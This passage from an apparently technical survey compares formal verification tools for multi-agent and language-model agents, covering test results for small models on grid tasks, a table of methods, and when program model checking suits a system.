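| DeepSeek-R1 1.5B | 0 | 0.98 | No result after 5 hours |
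| Llama 3.2 3B | 1 | 0.97 | 0.15 |
| Gemma 3n | 1 | 0.96 | 0 |
| Gemma 3 4B | 0 | 0.96 | 0 |
| Mistral 7B | 1 | 0 | 0 |
| Reinforcement learning | 0 | 0.18 | 0 |

Mistral's perfect score on the lake is less impressive than it looks because the agent reached only four states, with ten transitions between them. An agent that always answers "up" at the upper edge of the grid would produce this result, since it slides sideways forever and reaches neither the water nor the goal. The taxi prompt only asks the model to reach the petrol station and doesn't mention passengers, so a taxi can count as safe in this test without delivering anybody. DeepSeek's taxi result also includes two invalid answers.

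The largest model that the tool completed had 691 states and took 11 minutes. Running the language models took most of the time. DeepSeek needed more than four hours for the 17 states of the frozen lake, because it reasons at length before it answers.

The results are exact, but only for one language model with one prompt format and a fixed random seed, which makes the same prompt always produce the same answer. If the deployed model samples its answers at random, it may occasionally choose an action that the check did not cover. Gross and colleagues suggest that access to the model's word probabilities might make it possible to check random behaviour as well.

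The restriction to agents without memory is harder to remove. If robot A's prompt also contained the ten latest combinations of positions, it could have up to 9¹⁰, or about 3.5 billion, different prompts. A customer-service agent reads free text, so nobody could list all its prompts. The tested models are also small and old, so their accident rates don't show how current models would behave.

### The methods side by side

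The sizes for the last four methods in the table come from published examples and are not hard limits.

| Method | Object checked | Properties | Size handled | Human effort | Trusted base | Use for language-model agents |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Spin, NuSMV | Hand-written model | LTL, in NuSMV also CTL | Up to hundreds of millions of states | Writing the model, sometimes for weeks | Model and checker | Good for the software around the language model |
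| Reactive synthesis | Specification | LTL or GR(1) | Small for LTL, larger for GR(1) | Writing a complete specification | Specification and synthesis tool | Can produce a gatekeeper |
| MCMAS | Hand-written model with each agent's observations | CTL, knowledge, strategic ability | Grows exponentially with the number of agents | Writing the model | Model and checker | Could show what an attacker can force |
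| PRISM, LISA | Probabilistic model, generated from the program in LISA | Probabilities and expected costs | Up to hundreds of millions of states | Finding realistic probabilities | Probabilities, compiler and checker | Limited, since the probabilities of answers are rarely known |
| Any number of agents | Description of identical agents | Mainly safety | Unlimited number of simple agents | Finding an abstraction or cutoff | Abstraction and its proof | Only for the protocol between agents |
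| Swarm languages | Swarm program translated into C or a similar language | Mainly safety | Fixed number of agents, often a limited number of steps | Writing the program and rules | Translator and verifier | Little |
| vGOAL | Agent program translated into a model | CTL and probabilities | 45,743 states | Writing the program and rules | Interpreter, translator and checker | None so far |
| Language model as policy | Language model with its prompt and parser | Probabilities | 691 states | Modelling the task | Task model, fixed seed and checker | Direct, but only without memory |
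| AJPF | Agent program and its interpreter | LTL with beliefs, goals and actions | About 24,000 states | Modelling the environment | Interpreter, JPF and environment model | Not for the language model itself |
| Soteria | Generated plan | Contracts and rules about the order of calls | Plans with around ten states | Writing contracts and rules | Contracts, Dafny and monitor | Good if the agent can plan ahead |

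### When to use a virtual machine

Checking a program on a virtual machine is the better choice when the program already exists, its decisions are the main source of risk, and the company will run the same code it checks. A small BDI agent that supervises a robot typically meets these conditions. The method is also useful when mistakes depend on the exact order of the agents' steps, because a person writing a model can easily merge two steps that should be separate.

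Program model checking is a poor choice before a program exists. A protocol such as the corridor lock is easier to correct in a one-page NuSMV model than in two finished robots. A virtual machine that explores one state at a time is also too slow for large groups of agents, and it cannot verify a system with an unlimited number of them. Checking deadlines or what an opponent can force requires other tools, as does checking probabilities, even if AJPF has generated the model.

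A virtual machine cannot explore every answer a language model might give, but it can check each tool call before the call takes effect. This is the best use of the method for an agent whose next step depends on text it has not read yet. If the agent can write a complete plan, a verifier such as Soteria can find problems earlier, including dead ends.

These methods can also be combined. For the corridor, NuSMV could verify that the robots never collide if each enters only while it holds the lock. AJPF could then check each robot separately, verifying that it enters only when it believes it holds the lock. This avoids searching both programs together. The engineers would still have to show that a robot never believes it holds the lock when it doesn't. Dennis and colleagues don't regard their framework as essential to their approach to verifying an agent's decisions, so another checker could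 replace AJPF if it can examine the agent's beliefs and choices.
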